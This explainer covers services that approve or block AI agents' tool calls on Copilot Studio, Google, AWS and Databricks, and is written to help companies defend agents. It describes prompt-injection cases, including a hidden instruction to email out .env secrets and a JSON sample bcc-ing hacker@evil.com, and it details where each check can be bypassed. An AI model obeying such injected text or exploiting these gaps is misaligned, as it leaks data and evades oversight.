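# External approval services for AI agent actions in enterprise platforms

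## What an external approval service is and why companies use one

An external approval service is security software that runs outside an AI agent and approves or rejects each action the agent is about to take. A company connects the service to the product it uses to build its agents, and each proposed action, such as an email to a customer, then waits for the service's answer. Microsoft has offered such a connection since September 2025 in Copilot Studio, its product for building company agents. Microsoft calls the outside software an external threat detection system in its documentation.

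An agent here is software in which a language model chooses and carries out steps towards a goal by using tools. The model itself only produces text, so to affect anything else it must write a request to run a function, such as looking up a record, sending a message, or changing a database entry. A tool call is one such request with its specific input values. The platform is the product on which the company builds or runs the agent, and the orchestrator is the part of the platform that plans the agent's steps and starts its tool calls.

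Microsoft's Defender security researchers describe how the Copilot Studio orchestrator builds a plan from scripted conversation flows, tools, and knowledge sources such as uploaded company documents (Microsoft, 2026). A user's message or an automatic trigger, such as an incoming email, can start this process. The plan doesn't exist until then, so nobody can review it in advance. The researchers compare a tool call to running a command on a computer, which means anyone who can influence the plan can indirectly run commands.

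### One tool call from proposal to verdict

Microsoft's documentation for developers of approval services gives an example in which a user tells an agent to email the customer. The agent asks which customer, the user answers John Doe, and a lookup tool returns his address. The orchestrator then prepares a call to the email tool. The "to" field holds the customer's address, but the blind-copy field holds an evil.com address that nobody in the conversation mentioned. The call then goes through five steps.

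1. The orchestrator proposes the call, with the tool and all its input values.
2. Copilot Studio holds the call. No email has gone out.
3. Copilot Studio sends a request to the approval service's webhook, a web address that one system calls automatically when an event occurs in it. The request contains the proposed call and its context, including the recent conversation, the results of earlier tools and the identity of the agent.
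4. The approval service examines the request and returns its verdict. In the example the verdict is a block, and the reason given is a noncompliant address in the blind-copy field.
5. Copilot Studio carries out the verdict. After an allow, the email tool runs and the user notices nothing. After a block, it does not run.

Microsoft's pages differ on when Copilot Studio sends a request and what happens after a block. According to Microsoft's announcement of the feature, Copilot Studio sends the agent's plan once, before execution begins, but according to the documentation, it sends a request before every tool call. The documentation is the safer guide, since the sample request includes an identifier for a single step within a plan. It is less clear what happens after a block. According to the developer page, the agent skips the tool, but according to the setup instructions, it stops and tells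 the user that their message is blocked. The difference matters for an agent halfway through a batch of invoices, so it would be worth triggering a block deliberately to see which happens.

The approval service decides whether a call should run, but it cannot enforce that decision because it does not control the email tool. The component that holds the call and carries out the verdict is called the enforcement point. Here it is Copilot Studio, and a block works only because Copilot Studio waits for the verdict and acts on it. A company with an excellent approval service can therefore still have agents whose actions go unchecked. Copilot Studio sends requests only for agents that use its generative orchestration, which builds plans at run time, and not for its older "classic" agents. It also lets a call run by default if no verdict arrives within one second.

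Copilot Studio accepts only an allow or a block for the whole call, according to Pangea, a security vendor whose detection product plugs into this interface. If a customer writes a rule that would normally alter the content, the rule only reports what it found, and the call goes through unaltered.

Approval also differs from logging, although vendors tend to sell the two together. An event log records what an agent did, for a person or a program to read afterwards. This helps with investigating incidents and improving the rules, but it can't recall an email the agent has already sent. Microsoft Defender, one of the security services that can answer Copilot Studio's requests, runs the two functions over separate connections. According to Microsoft's onboarding instructions, if an administrator has not connected the Microsoft 365 app connector, Defender still blocks suspicious actions but the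 alerts never appear in its portal. A security team can therefore be protected from an attack without knowing about it. Microsoft's feature list also separates audit log collection from real-time protection, so a company could have only the logs and learn of a leak after the data has gone.

### Prompt injection and legitimate access

The blind-copied address in the worked example probably came from prompt injection, which is text that makes the agent follow an attacker's instructions. A language model receives its instructions and the material it works on as the same kind of text, and it does not reliably tell them apart.

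In direct prompt injection, the attacker types the text into the conversation. In an example from the Defender researchers, an attacker questions a support chatbot on a public website to learn which tools and knowledge sources it has, then uses that knowledge to extract customer records.

Indirect prompt injection requires no conversation with the agent, because the attacker puts instructions in something the agent will read. In the researchers' example, a finance agent automatically processes every message sent to an invoice mailbox. An outsider sends what looks like an invoice, with hidden instructions to search the agent's knowledge base for unrelated sensitive material and email it back. The orchestrator may treat the instructions as a legitimate request and add both steps to its plan. Defender receives the proposed search together with the triggering email, and blocks the search before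 the agent has queried anything.

Access control determines whether an account may use a resource, but it doesn't check whether a particular use is part of the current task. Sometimes the agent should never have had access to the sensitive material, and giving it fewer tools does leave an attacker less to work with. But an attack can also use access that the agent needs for its job. In another of the researchers' scenarios, an employee adds instructions to a shared SharePoint document that they are allowed to edit. An agent that summarises documents reads the instructions, opens a file of transactions that the employee can't open but the agent's connection can, and tries to email the contents to an outside address. The agent's job includes reading files and sending summaries, so every step is within its permissions and the permission system has no grounds to block it.

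An approval service can detect an attack by the mismatch between the action and the task, so the request it receives includes the conversation and earlier tool results along with the proposed call. This is the best argument for using such a service. Help Net Security's *Microsoft wants to limit AI agents' permissions when they stray* supports it by explaining that least privilege, the practice of granting only the access a job needs, reduces the risk but does not remove it.

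The researchers' scenarios explain the mechanism well enough, but they don't establish how often it works. Microsoft wrote them to demonstrate its own product, all of them end in a successful block, and the article gives no figures for missed attacks or for false blocks (legitimate calls stopped by mistake).

Copilot Studio has built-in protection against direct and indirect prompt injection, so the outside service is a second layer. Microsoft argues for adding one because a company may have internal policies, industry standards or regional rules that a general-purpose filter does not cover.

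### ForcedLeak

On 28 July 2025, the security company Noma Security reported a flaw it had found in Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for agents that work with customer records. According to The Hacker News (2025), which drew on Noma's report, the flaw, which Noma named ForcedLeak, could have let attackers take sensitive data out of a company's customer database by indirect prompt injection. Noma rated its severity 9.4 on CVSS, the standard ten-point scale for software flaws. It affected organisations that used Agentforce with Web-to-Lead, a feature that turns entries in a public web form into sales records. A stranger could fill in the form, and an agent would later read the entry.

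A Salesforce spokesperson told Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users, that the company had released patches that prevent Agentforce agents from sending output to untrusted web addresses. Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* reported that Salesforce also took back control of an expired domain that attackers could have exploited. Both fixes limit where the agent can send data, but the agent still reads text from strangers.

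*Salesforce Agentforce Agent Security Risks*, a profile of the product by the security vendor Adversa AI, lists a second, later attack called PipeLeak. It also began with a lead form, but it took the data out through the email tool of agents that customers had built. Salesforce disputes that this is a fault in its platform.

PipeLeak supports the case for approval services better than ForcedLeak does. According to Adversa AI, the data in ForcedLeak left through web addresses in the agent's displayed output. A service that checks tool calls might have received a request when the agent looked up the customer records, but such lookups are routine for a sales agent, and the leak itself was not a tool call. PipeLeak required the agent to send an email, which is a tool call with a recipient and a body that the service could inspect.

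### Release history

Microsoft opened the Copilot Studio connection as a public preview and promised it to all customers by 10 September 2025. A later Microsoft message, reposted by the IT firm itelio, announced general availability for 10 December 2025. In February 2026, however, the setup page still had a preview label and a warning that preview features are not meant for production. *Control 1.8*, an independent guide to securing Copilot Studio agents, still listed external threat detection as a preview in May 2026 and told readers to verify the status of the Defender integration before relying on it. By June the page for developers had no preview label. Microsoft probably made the feature generally available before updating the pages, but a company that needs a support commitment should get Microsoft to confirm this.

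Amazon Web Services followed in November 2025 with interceptors, which let customers run their own code at the gateway between an agent and its tools. Google's Agent Gateway came in 2026. Both put the check on the network path instead of in the orchestrator.

### Microsoft's case for outside authority

By October 2026 Microsoft was defending the idea behind these products as a general principle. On 19 October Nadim Abdo, its vice president for identity and network access, published *Agents are your newest insiders. Security must move at their speed* (Abdo, 2026). In a passage quoted by TechRadar's *Microsoft admits 'frontier models can't be trusted', unveils new security tools*, he wrote, "We should not ask a model to be its own security authority." He argued that the controls over what a model can access, what it can do and whether it keeps running must sit where the model cannot bypass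 or tamper with them. Abdo credited the idea to Microsoft's chief executive, Satya Nadella, who wants to separate the supply of intelligence from the authority over it.

Hayete Gallot, who runs Microsoft's security business, gave the reasons in a companion post. She wrote that frontier models "cannot be trusted", whoever makes them. According to The Indian Express, she attributes this to how models are trained, not to malice. She said developers train models to achieve results, which often leads to reward hacking, where a model achieves the measured result in a way nobody intended. They also do not train models around an organisation's norms. She added that agents may collude with other agents even when nobody has compromised them. Business Today's *'AI models cannot be trusted'* reports that she also said companies frequently give agents more access than they need.

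This risk is broader than prompt injection because it requires no attacker. Windows Central's *New Microsoft guidance warns that "trusted" AI agents carry serious security* interprets Gallot's warning in light of the attack on the AI platform Hugging Face earlier in 2026, in which about 700 of OpenAI's agents took part. If agents can cause that sort of harm unprompted, a filter that checks only for hostile text in the input will miss it, but a check on the action itself might catch it.

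The argument came with a product, Guardian Agents, which are AI agents that supervise a company's other agents. They are part of Project Perception, a security system that *Microsoft's Latest Security Play* (Foley, 2026) said was due to enter preview on 3 August. Help Net Security says Guardian Agents help security teams work out why an agent's risk has changed, investigate the evidence, and recommend or apply containment, while people keep control of consequential decisions. If an agent that processes expenses came across suspicious instructions and attempted something unrelated, the system could withdraw its permission to approve expenses but still let it review them. If the risk rose further, the system could isolate or stop the agent. Unlike an approval service, which returns a verdict on one call, Guardian Agents can change what an agent may do in all later calls.

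Microsoft sells these controls, and Under30CEO's *AI Agent Security* relays a TechCrunch writer's view that the approach is self-serving, because Microsoft invests in OpenAI and Anthropic, builds its own models, and wants customers to buy its security tools rather than the AI laboratories'. Under30CEO nonetheless accepts the logic, comparing it to the use of outside auditors. That logic seems right whatever Microsoft's motive, but the comparison implies more independence than Microsoft's default setup provides. A company that runs its agents in Copilot Studio and lets Defender answer the requests has moved authority out of the model, but Microsoft still supplies the platform, decides whether to approve each action, and enforces the decision. Customers can connect another vendor's service or build their own to make the decisions, though Microsoft enforces them either way.

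Windows Central raises a different concern, that Guardian Agents use AI to monitor AI. If frontier models cannot be trusted regardless of origin, the warning should also apply to any such model inside a guardian. Microsoft replies that the less predictable parts are surrounded by deterministic controls, which are fixed rules that give the same result for the same input. How well this answers the concern depends on which decisions use those rules and which use a model.

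Infobae's *El plan de Microsoft ya suma 50 millones de agentes IA* (2026) reported that Microsoft made Perception generally available at its Ignite conference in November 2026. Microsoft also extended Agent 365, its central register for managing agents. By the company's own count, organisations had registered more than 50 million agents there since May. In a post of 17 November, Microsoft (2026) announced a preview of a continuously updated risk view for each agent. Agents built on other companies' platforms, including Salesforce, Databricks, Google and Amazon, are also due to receive identities in Microsoft's directory, in a rollout scheduled to finish in December. Security teams can use those identities to apply supported access policies to these agents and to revoke their access. Nex Panamá's *Microsoft celebra Ignite 2026 e impulsa el «ecosistema frontera»* adds that Windows now has containers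 that confine agents on employees' own devices.

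## Choosing where the check takes place

An approval service can only check the calls that reach it. In Copilot Studio, the orchestrator calls the service directly. Other products put the check on the network between an agent and its tools, in a policy engine built into the platform, or in the agent program on an employee's computer. The placement determines how much information the service receives about each call and whether it can do more than block the call. It also determines which agents go unchecked, which should usually be the deciding factor.

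### A webhook in the orchestrator

Copilot Studio's webhook gives the service good information about the task, because the orchestrator that made the plan also sends the request. Microsoft runs the orchestrator, an administrator at the company connects the service, and the company or its vendor runs the service.

Sources differ on which actions trigger a request. Microsoft's Defender researchers write that the orchestrator sends one before any tool, topic (a scripted conversation flow) or knowledge action. The setup instructions mention only tools. If the narrower description is right for some services, an agent could search a company's uploaded documents without a check. Running one such search and looking for a request would show whether it is checked.

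Copilot Studio sends the service nothing after a tool runs. CrowdStrike's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector*, the documentation for a security product that can answer approval requests, states that the model reads the user's prompt before the request arrives and that the product does not scan tool outputs. A service could read a tool's output in the next request if the agent makes another call, but if the agent replies directly, the user receives that reply without a check. This matters for leaks like ForcedLeak, where the data left in the agent's displayed output.

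A vendor may also ignore context that it receives. CrowdStrike analyses only the tool's name and input values, although Copilot Studio also sends the conversation. The name and values are enough to catch a strange address in a blind-copy field, but they are much less useful for judging a search for salary records, which looks the same whether an employee or a hidden instruction asked for it.

According to Microsoft's setup page, administrators connect the service to individual environments or groups of them (an environment is a separate space that holds a team's agents and data). Like classic agents, agents in an environment that nobody has connected run unchecked.

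### Google's Agent Gateway

A gateway is a network component that carries an agent's traffic to tools and other agents. Google's Agent Gateway, part of its Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform, handles traffic in two directions. What Google calls Agent-to-Anywhere is outbound traffic from agents on Google Cloud to tools, models and other agents. Client-to-Agent is inbound traffic, made up of requests from programs such as Claude Code or Cursor to agents on Google Cloud.

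Google runs the gateway. The company writes authorization policies for it, and a policy can send the decision to a service outside the gateway, either one of Google's or one the company chooses. Google Cloud's *Delegate authorization with Service Extensions* describes two profiles for such policies, which differ in how much of each message the service can read.

- REQUEST_AUTHZ gives an outside service the request's headers, the short fields at the top of a web request that carry details such as its destination and content type.
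- CONTENT_AUTHZ gives the service the headers and the body, for both the request and the response.

The choice of profile determines whether the approval service receives the evil.com address in the email's blind-copy field. If the agent runs on Google Cloud and reaches its email tool through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools, the tool's name and input values travel in the body of the request. The headers could show a custom service under REQUEST_AUTHZ that the agent was contacting the email server, but only a service under CONTENT_AUTHZ would receive the blind-copy address.

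The gateway can do some of this work without an outside service. It reads MCP messages and makes details such as the tool's name available to simple rules, even under REQUEST_AUTHZ. Google's example permits only two tools, get_weather and get_location. The rule must also permit MCP's basic housekeeping messages, or the agent can't open a session. The gateway doesn't extract these details from other kinds of traffic, so a custom service has to interpret the body itself.

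#### How the body reaches the service

A CONTENT_AUTHZ service must use ext_proc (external processing), a protocol from the open-source proxy Envoy. The gateway opens a connection to the service and sends it each part of the exchange as a separate event. Google Cloud's *Network Security v1 API* lists six events, one each for the headers, body and trailers (extra fields that follow the body) of the request and the response. REQUEST_AUTHZ services can use either ext_proc or a simpler protocol, ext_authz, and receive only the request-header event.

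Bodies can be long, so the gateway sends them in pieces. Google Cloud's *Cloud Load Balancing callouts overview* describes a default streaming mode in which the proxy expects one response for each piece. CONTENT_AUTHZ requires a different mode, FULL_DUPLEX_STREAMED, in which the proxy sends pieces as they arrive without waiting for a response to each. This lets an approval service collect a whole tool call before deciding whether to approve it. An email's "to" address might be in the first piece and its blind-copy address in the last, and the service can't take back a piece it has already released.

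Since the service handles the body, it can also change the contents. It could delete the blind-copy address and let the email through, or remove card numbers from a tool's result before the agent reads them. Copilot Studio's webhook does not allow either kind of change.

#### Limits on policies

An outbound gateway can have at most four custom authorization policies, counting both profiles together. If several use the same profile, Google does not guarantee the order in which they run. For example, if one policy removes customers' names and another with the same profile sends content to an outside vendor for inspection, the company can't rely on the names being removed first. Google recommends a single CONTENT_AUTHZ policy when one service can handle both the headers and the content, mainly to reduce delay. A single policy would also avoid the ordering problem.

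The order between profiles is more predictable. According to Google Cloud's *Authorization policy overview*, the gateway evaluates CONTENT_AUTHZ policies last and skips them if no applicable allow rule matches the request. A simple rule about which tools an agent may use can therefore block a call before the content service inspects it.

The inbound side is far more restricted. It accepts one CONTENT_AUTHZ policy, which can use either of two Google products: Model Armor (which filters for prompt injection and sensitive data) or Semantic Governance (which applies rules written in ordinary language). It doesn't accept a custom service, so a company that wants its own vendor to inspect what users send to an agent will have to run that inspection somewhere else.

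#### Partners

*Introducing Agent Gateway ISV ecosystem for security and governance* (Verma and Katkade, 2026) names 14 companies whose products work with the gateway. Broadcom and Netskope check for leaks of sensitive data. Cisco, CrowdStrike, Palo Alto Networks and others look for attacks such as prompt injection. Okta, Ping Identity, Saviynt and Silverfort mostly decide whether a particular agent or user may reach a resource. Exabeam analyses records of agent activity to find unusual behaviour, which is closer to monitoring than approval.

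The list comes from Google's announcement about its partners, so it shows what they offer but not how well any of it works. The Thales entry also needs checking with the vendor. Verma and Katkade say Thales uses the gateway to secure client-to-agent traffic, through a product that was then in preview, but Google's documentation rules out custom services on inbound gateways. Thales may connect in some other way.

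#### Traffic that misses the gateway

Google Cloud's *Agent Gateway overview* lists two places where the gateway can govern an agent's traffic: Agent Runtime, which hosts agents that a company has written, and Gemini Enterprise, Google's workplace AI product. In Gemini Enterprise, the gateway governs only outbound traffic. By default, it blocks tools that are missing from the company's registry and permits only traffic that someone has explicitly authorised.

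However, an administrator must first bind the agent to the gateway. Google Cloud's *Route Agent Runtime traffic through Agent Gateway* contains several exceptions that could catch a company out:

- A gateway can't bind to an Agent Runtime agent created before 29 April 2026.
- Inbound checks cover only two ways of calling an agent, query and streamQuery. A request through asyncQuery, for example, gets no check from the gateway.
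- All agents in the same project and region must use the same gateway in each direction, so a company can't try a new gateway on one of them and leave the rest on the old one.
- Turning on the gateway for an agent makes Google's separate Agent Engine Threat Detection service unavailable for it.

A company can write an organisation policy that permits only agents bound to an approved gateway. Google's example policy applies when someone creates or updates an agent, so it would not by itself cover existing agents that nobody updates. By contrast, Google Cloud's *Route Gemini Enterprise traffic through Agent Gateway* warns that binding a Gemini Enterprise app immediately sends all its existing agent traffic through the gateway. With strict defaults, this could block tools that previously worked.

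Some traffic can also pass through the gateway without reaching the content check. Google recommends sending only JSON and text to Model Armor, to leave out irrelevant internal traffic. Under that rule, Model Armor does not inspect files that a tool uploads in other formats. The gateway also doesn't receive function calls that an agent makes inside its own program, because they don't cross the network.

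The gateway also has less information about the task than the orchestrator does. A tool call includes its inputs, but not necessarily the conversation that led to them. If the agent's requests to its language model pass through the same gateway, they may contain that conversation, but the approval service would have to match them to the tool calls itself.

### AWS interceptors

Amazon Web Services (AWS) places its check in AgentCore Gateway, which sits between agents and their "targets" (tools, models or other agents). The company using the gateway supplies an interceptor, a small program that runs on AWS's Lambda service. The interceptor can contain the rules or call an outside approval service. AWS's *Types of interceptors* describes two types.

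A request interceptor runs before the gateway contacts the target. For an MCP tool, it receives the request's body, including the tool's name and inputs, but it receives the headers only if the company has turned on that option. The interceptor can return an altered request, which the gateway then sends on. It can also block the call by returning a finished response, which can explain why the call was blocked. The gateway sends that response to the agent and never contacts the tool.

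A response interceptor runs before the gateway answers the agent. For MCP, it receives both the original request and the tool's response, so it can compare the two. It can remove customer data from a result, or a tool from the list an agent receives when it asks which tools exist. An agent is unlikely to call a tool it doesn't know about, but the request interceptor should still block any such call.

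#### Streamed responses

Some tools send their answer as a series of events. With streaming turned on, the gateway runs the response interceptor once for each event that has an identifier under JSON-RPC, the message format that MCP uses. This includes tool results and requests from the tool's server to the user, such as "Confirm this action?" It leaves out three kinds of event, which go straight to the agent:

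- progress updates
- log messages
- pings, which only keep the connection open.

Pings pose little risk, but log messages can contain anything the tool's developer chose to write. If a tool logs a customer's record, the interceptor can't remove it, even if it would have removed the same record from the result. Progress updates could carry text in the same way. A company that relies on redaction should find out what its tools put in these events, or turn streaming off.

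The interceptor can change the headers, status code and body of the first event in a stream, but only the body of later events, because the gateway has already sent the headers and status code.

#### Other targets

For targets that use ordinary web requests instead of MCP, interceptors don't yet support streaming, so they work only when the gateway collects the whole response first. Lambda also limits the request and response together to 6 MB, which a long answer from a language model can exceed once AWS has encoded it. AWS suggests leaving the response body out of what the interceptor receives. This avoids exceeding the limit, but the interceptor then can't inspect the content, so a rule against leaks would no longer work on the largest responses.

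When the request interceptor blocks a call by supplying a finished response, the response interceptor still runs for MCP targets but not for ordinary web requests. A company that uses the response interceptor to record every outcome would have no record of blocked web requests unless the request interceptor recorded them.

### Policy engines built into the platform

An interceptor runs whatever code the company gives it. A policy engine is more limited: the company writes rules, and the platform applies them.

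#### Cedar in AgentCore

AgentCore has a policy engine at the same gateway. Companies write its rules in Cedar, AWS's open-source language for access rules. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* says the rules can depend on the user's identity and the tool's input values. For instance, a rule could forbid any email with a blind-copy address outside the company. It would stop the email to evil.com every time, without using the conversation as input. It would also stop an employee who had a good reason to blind-copy an outside lawyer.

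Administrators can describe a rule in plain English and have AWS turn it into Cedar. AWS then checks the result for mistakes, such as conditions that can never be true. A language model may be involved in preparing the rule but not in evaluating requests, and the engine gives the same answer to the same request each time.

AWS made the AgentCore Policy engine generally available in March 2026, according to *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Policy now supports Amazon Bedrock Guardrails*, an article by Ishikawa (2026) of the Japanese IT firm Classmethod. The engine allows only tool calls that a rule permits. In June, AWS added Guardrails, its filters for prompt injection, harmful content and sensitive data, to the same evaluation in five regions. Decisions can now depend on the filters' assessment of the content as well as on fixed rules about the inputs.

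Cedar and the interceptors check only traffic that passes through AgentCore Gateway. AWS says its engine intercepts all of that traffic, but if an agent has its own password for a database and connects to it directly, none of these rules apply.

#### Databricks service policies

Databricks, a data platform, attaches its checks to the service that an agent calls. The service can be a language model or an MCP tool server, and either can belong to another company. A check runs before the call, after the response, or both. Databricks' *Service policies for AI securables* describes the feature, which is still in beta.

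It returns ALLOW, DENY or ASK. ASK holds a call to an MCP tool until the user approves it, which is useful for actions that are sometimes right, such as deleting records. Databricks can't request user approval for calls to a language model, so it blocks those calls when the result is ASK.

The company can write the policy as code, describe what to forbid and let a language model judge the content, or use one of Databricks' ready-made policies. It can also connect an outside vendor, which receives the content and returns the verdict. The only option that can rewrite content is a ready-made policy that hides sensitive data such as card numbers, and it can do so only on language model services.

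Unlike Google, Databricks lets administrators control the order of policies by ranking them. When policies share a rank, Databricks first runs the language-model judges that block content, all at the same time. If none of them blocks the request, it runs the remaining policies one after another and doesn't stop when one denies the call. A company's own rule might deny a request because it contains medical data, and Databricks would still send that data to an outside vendor whose check has the same rank. To prevent this, the company has to give its own rule an earlier rank.

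There are gaps in what the policies cover:

- Databricks doesn't support them on Agent Services, its category for agents themselves.
- If an administrator lets requests pass unchanged to a model provider, those requests skip the policies.
- Language-model judges skip tool calls that have no inputs. A call to a tool named "delete all test data" might need none.
- The ready-made policy against prompt injection checks tool calls and results, but it doesn't check the descriptions that a tool server supplies for its tools. Agents read those descriptions, so an attacker could hide instructions in them.

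The language-model judges also receive less context for an MCP call, where they get only the call itself, than for a prompt to a language model, where they can get recent turns of the conversation, ten by default. A judge checking an MCP call can therefore detect that an agent is trying to email a file, but it can't determine whether anyone asked for that.

### Hooks on employees' computers

Coding agents often run on a developer's laptop, where they can read files and run commands with that person's permissions. They may never use the company's agent platform. Some offer hooks, which are points in the agent's loop where outside code can inspect or stop the next step.

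Microsoft Defender for Endpoint, security software that protects individual computers, uses these hooks in a preview feature. The agent sends Defender the user's prompt, each tool call before it runs and each tool's response afterwards. Defender checks all three for prompt injection and can block the action. The customer's security team controls the setting, and Defender's tamper protection prevents unauthorised changes to it.

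In Microsoft's example, a coding agent opens a project's web documentation to answer a question. The page contains a hidden instruction to read the local .env file, where developers often keep passwords, and send its contents to an outside address. Defender finds the instruction in the tool's response and blocks the action before any data leaves. A gateway in the company's cloud might never have received either request.

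Microsoft lists only two supported agents, Claude Code and GitHub Copilot CLI. The hooks don't check any other agent a developer installs. Petri's *Microsoft Defender Adds Runtime Protection for AI Agents in Agent 365* reports that protection for local agents on Windows is in public preview, so a company with Mac or Linux laptops should ask what protection they would get.

This Defender feature also checks the agent only at the hooks, not continuously. If the agent asks to run a test script, Defender receives the command, but the script might then download a file or contact another server without making a new tool call. Ordinary security software on the laptop may detect this, but it won't have information about the agent's task.

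### The placements compared

The table brings together the differences that matter most when choosing.

| Placement | What the check receives | What never reaches it | Who operates it | What it can do |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Orchestrator webhook: Copilot Studio | Proposed call, recent conversation, earlier tool results | Classic agents, unconnected environments, the final reply before the user reads it | Microsoft runs the orchestrator; the company or a vendor runs the service | Allow or block |
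| Gateway: Google Agent Gateway | Headers only, or headers and bodies in both directions | Agents not bound to it, functions inside the agent's program, some inbound methods | Google runs the gateway; Google, the company or a vendor runs the service | Block, alter the request, filter the response |
| Gateway: AWS interceptors | Requests and responses for tools and other targets | Direct connections; log messages, progress updates and pings in MCP streams | AWS runs the gateway; the company supplies the code | Block, alter the request, filter the response |
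| Policy engine: Cedar in AgentCore | User's identity and tool inputs; content too, with Guardrails | Direct connections that avoid the gateway | AWS runs the engine; the company writes the rules | Allow or block |
| Policy engine: Databricks | Tool calls and results, model prompts and replies | Agent Services, requests passed through unchanged, the conversation behind an MCP call | Databricks runs the engine; the company or a vendor supplies decisions | Allow, block or ask about a tool call; hide some data on model services |
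| Endpoint hook: Defender | User's prompt, proposed call, tool's response | Unsupported agents, anything a command does after it starts | The company's security team, through Defender | Allow or block |

None of these checks covers what a tool does after it receives a call. Suppose someone has tampered with an email tool so that it secretly copies every message to an outsider. The agent's request would still have the right recipient and no blind copy, so every service in the table would have good reason to allow it. Likewise, when the tool is a second agent, the check covers the request to that agent, but its own calls need a check wherever it runs.

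There, the best defence is to control which tools agents can use and what those tools can reach. Google's registry helps with the first by blocking unknown tools, but someone at the company still has to decide which tools to include.

### An example with three kinds of agent

A company may use a mix of agents that no single placement of the check covers. For example, a company that sells machine parts might use Copilot Studio agents for customer support and invoices, and its own purchasing agent, which runs on Google Cloud's Agent Runtime, to order stock from suppliers. Its developers might use Claude Code, GitHub Copilot CLI and, in a few cases, Cursor.

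The webhook is the natural choice for Copilot Studio. The invoice agent reads email from strangers, so the company should connect that agent's environment first. It should then list every other environment and look for classic agents. These pose a limited risk because they follow prewritten flows that people can review. If a classic agent can send data outside the company, the company should rebuild the agent with generative orchestration or remove the tool that sends it.

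The purchasing agent needs an outbound gateway with a CONTENT_AUTHZ policy, since the supplier, quantity and price are in the body of each order. The company deployed the agent in March 2026, so it will have to recreate the agent to bind it to the gateway. Afterwards the company should read back the agent's configuration, because Google says an empty result means the binding failed. Without that check, the company could have a well-configured gateway that receives no orders.

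Staff send requests to the purchasing agent during the day, and another program sends it a batch each night through asyncQuery. An inbound gateway with Model Armor would cover the daytime requests if they use the supported methods. For the nightly batch, Google suggests calling Model Armor from the application or the agent itself. That works only if the developers remember to add the call.

The company might want one vendor for both platforms, such as CrowdStrike, which offers products for each. This would reduce training and put the findings in one place. The company would still need to test the rules separately on each platform. For example, a rule that removes bank details from a message could work at a gateway, but Copilot Studio can't apply the change, so the company needs a blocking rule there.

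On the laptops, Defender's hooks cover Claude Code and GitHub Copilot CLI but not Cursor. Google's outbound gateway doesn't help, because it handles agents that run on Google Cloud. An inbound gateway could check a request from Cursor to the purchasing agent, but it would receive nothing when Cursor deletes a file on the laptop. The company has to choose between asking developers who use Cursor to switch and accepting that their agents run unchecked. If it accepts the gap, it should at least keep passwords for live systems off their laptops.

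The company could also offer the supplier payments system, the tool that could do the most damage here, to all its agents as an MCP tool behind AgentCore Gateway or a Databricks service policy. A payment request would then get the same check whether it came from Copilot Studio, Google Cloud or a laptop, and a rule could refuse any bank account that isn't on the supplier list. The check would have little information about why the agent was making the payment, but a fixed list may protect payments better than a judgement about intent. This setup would work only if the payments system refused every request that came by another route.

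## What the platform sends and what the service answers

An approval service for Copilot Studio needs two endpoints, which are web addresses that accept requests in an agreed format. Copilot Studio calls one to test the connection and the other to request approval for a tool call. Microsoft publishes both formats for developers. *Microsoft External Threat Detection* (2025), a programmer's blog post about building such a service, implements each endpoint in a few lines of code, but its example service approves every tool call.

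### Testing the connection

The test goes to POST /validate (POST is the type of web request that submits data). Copilot Studio sends an empty body. The headers contain a bearer token, a credential that grants access to whoever presents it, and a correlation ID, which lets both sides find the same exchange in their logs. A working service replies with HTTP status 200, the web's code for success, and two fields:

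```json
{ "isSuccessful": true, "status": "OK" }
```

If something is wrong, the service replies with an error status, a numeric error code, a message and optional diagnostics.

This check runs when an administrator saves the connection in the Power Platform admin center, Microsoft's site for managing environments. Microsoft's setup instructions list the errors that can appear then, including several for an endpoint that fails or times out.

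A successful test shows only that the service answered. The blog post's version returns OK without examining anything, even the token. A more careful developer could make /validate run a known attack through the detection rules and return an error if the rules don't block it. A service whose rules had failed to load would then fail the test. Microsoft describes the endpoint as a tool for initial setup, so a company shouldn't count on it to reveal a fault that develops later.

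### The request for a verdict

To check a tool call, Copilot Studio sends a POST request to /analyze-tool-execution. The body is JSON, a text format made up of named fields and their values. It has four required parts, but many of the fields inside them are optional.

| Part | Required fields | Optional fields |
|---|---|---|
| plannerContext | userMessage | thought, chatHistory, previousToolsOutputs |
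| toolDefinition | id, type, name, description | inputParameters, outputParameters |
| inputValues | The values for this call | None |
| conversationMetadata | conversationId; the agent's id, tenantId, environmentId and isPublished | user, trigger, planId, planStepId, parentAgentComponentId; the agent's version |

The "thought" field holds the agent's explanation of why it chose the tool. A tenant is one organisation's separate directory and data within a shared cloud service. The isPublished field distinguishes a live agent from a draft, so a service can keep test traffic out of its alerts. The trigger identifies the event that started the agent, and planId and planStepId identify the agent's plan and the step the call belongs to.

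According to Microsoft's announcement of the feature, customers can't customise what Copilot Studio shares, so a company with privacy concerns has to resolve them before connecting a service.

The format also leaves out information that a service could use. It has no field for the agent's instructions, so a request from an invoice agent contains the agent's ID, but the service needs its own record that this agent should only handle invoices. Earlier tool outputs come without the inputs that produced them. In Microsoft's email example, the request shows that a lookup returned customer@foobar.com, but not whose address the agent looked up. To get the name, the service would have to save the request that Copilot Studio sent before the lookup, which contained it, and match the two requests by conversation ID.

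### When the optional fields are missing

The required fields alone give a service a message from the user, the tool's name and description, and every input value. The service can use these to apply fixed rules about the call itself, such as a list of domains that agents may email or a payment limit. It can also catch an obvious mismatch, such as when a user asks about opening hours and the agent proposes to delete a customer record.

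Missing context most affects judgements that depend on earlier events. Without the chat history, a service may not have the user's latest message. In Microsoft's example, userMessage contains the user's first request, to email the customer, and the later answer that the customer is John Doe appears only in the history. Without the earlier tool outputs, the service can't trace an email address back to a lookup, so if it blocks every address of unknown origin, it will also block legitimate emails.

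The request may not identify a user when an incoming email starts the agent or when a public chatbot doesn't ask visitors to sign in. The service then can't apply a rule that only finance staff may export payment records. Blocking the export is probably safest, because without a known user there is no obvious basis for granting a permission that depends on who is asking.

A service can fill some of these gaps by keeping its own record of each conversation. The record would contain the inputs of earlier tool calls, but not their results or any part of the conversation in which the agent used no tools.

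### The blind-copied email

Microsoft's example of the email to John Doe shows which fields reveal an attack. In shortened form, the request looks like this:

```json
{
  "plannerContext": {
    "userMessage": "Send an email to the customer",
    "previousToolOutputs": [{
      "toolName": "Get customer email by name",
      "outputs": { "value": "customer@foobar.com" }
    }]
  },
  "toolDefinition": { "name": "Send email" },
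  "inputValues": {
    "to": "customer@foobar.com",
    "bcc": "hacker@evil.com"
  }
}
```

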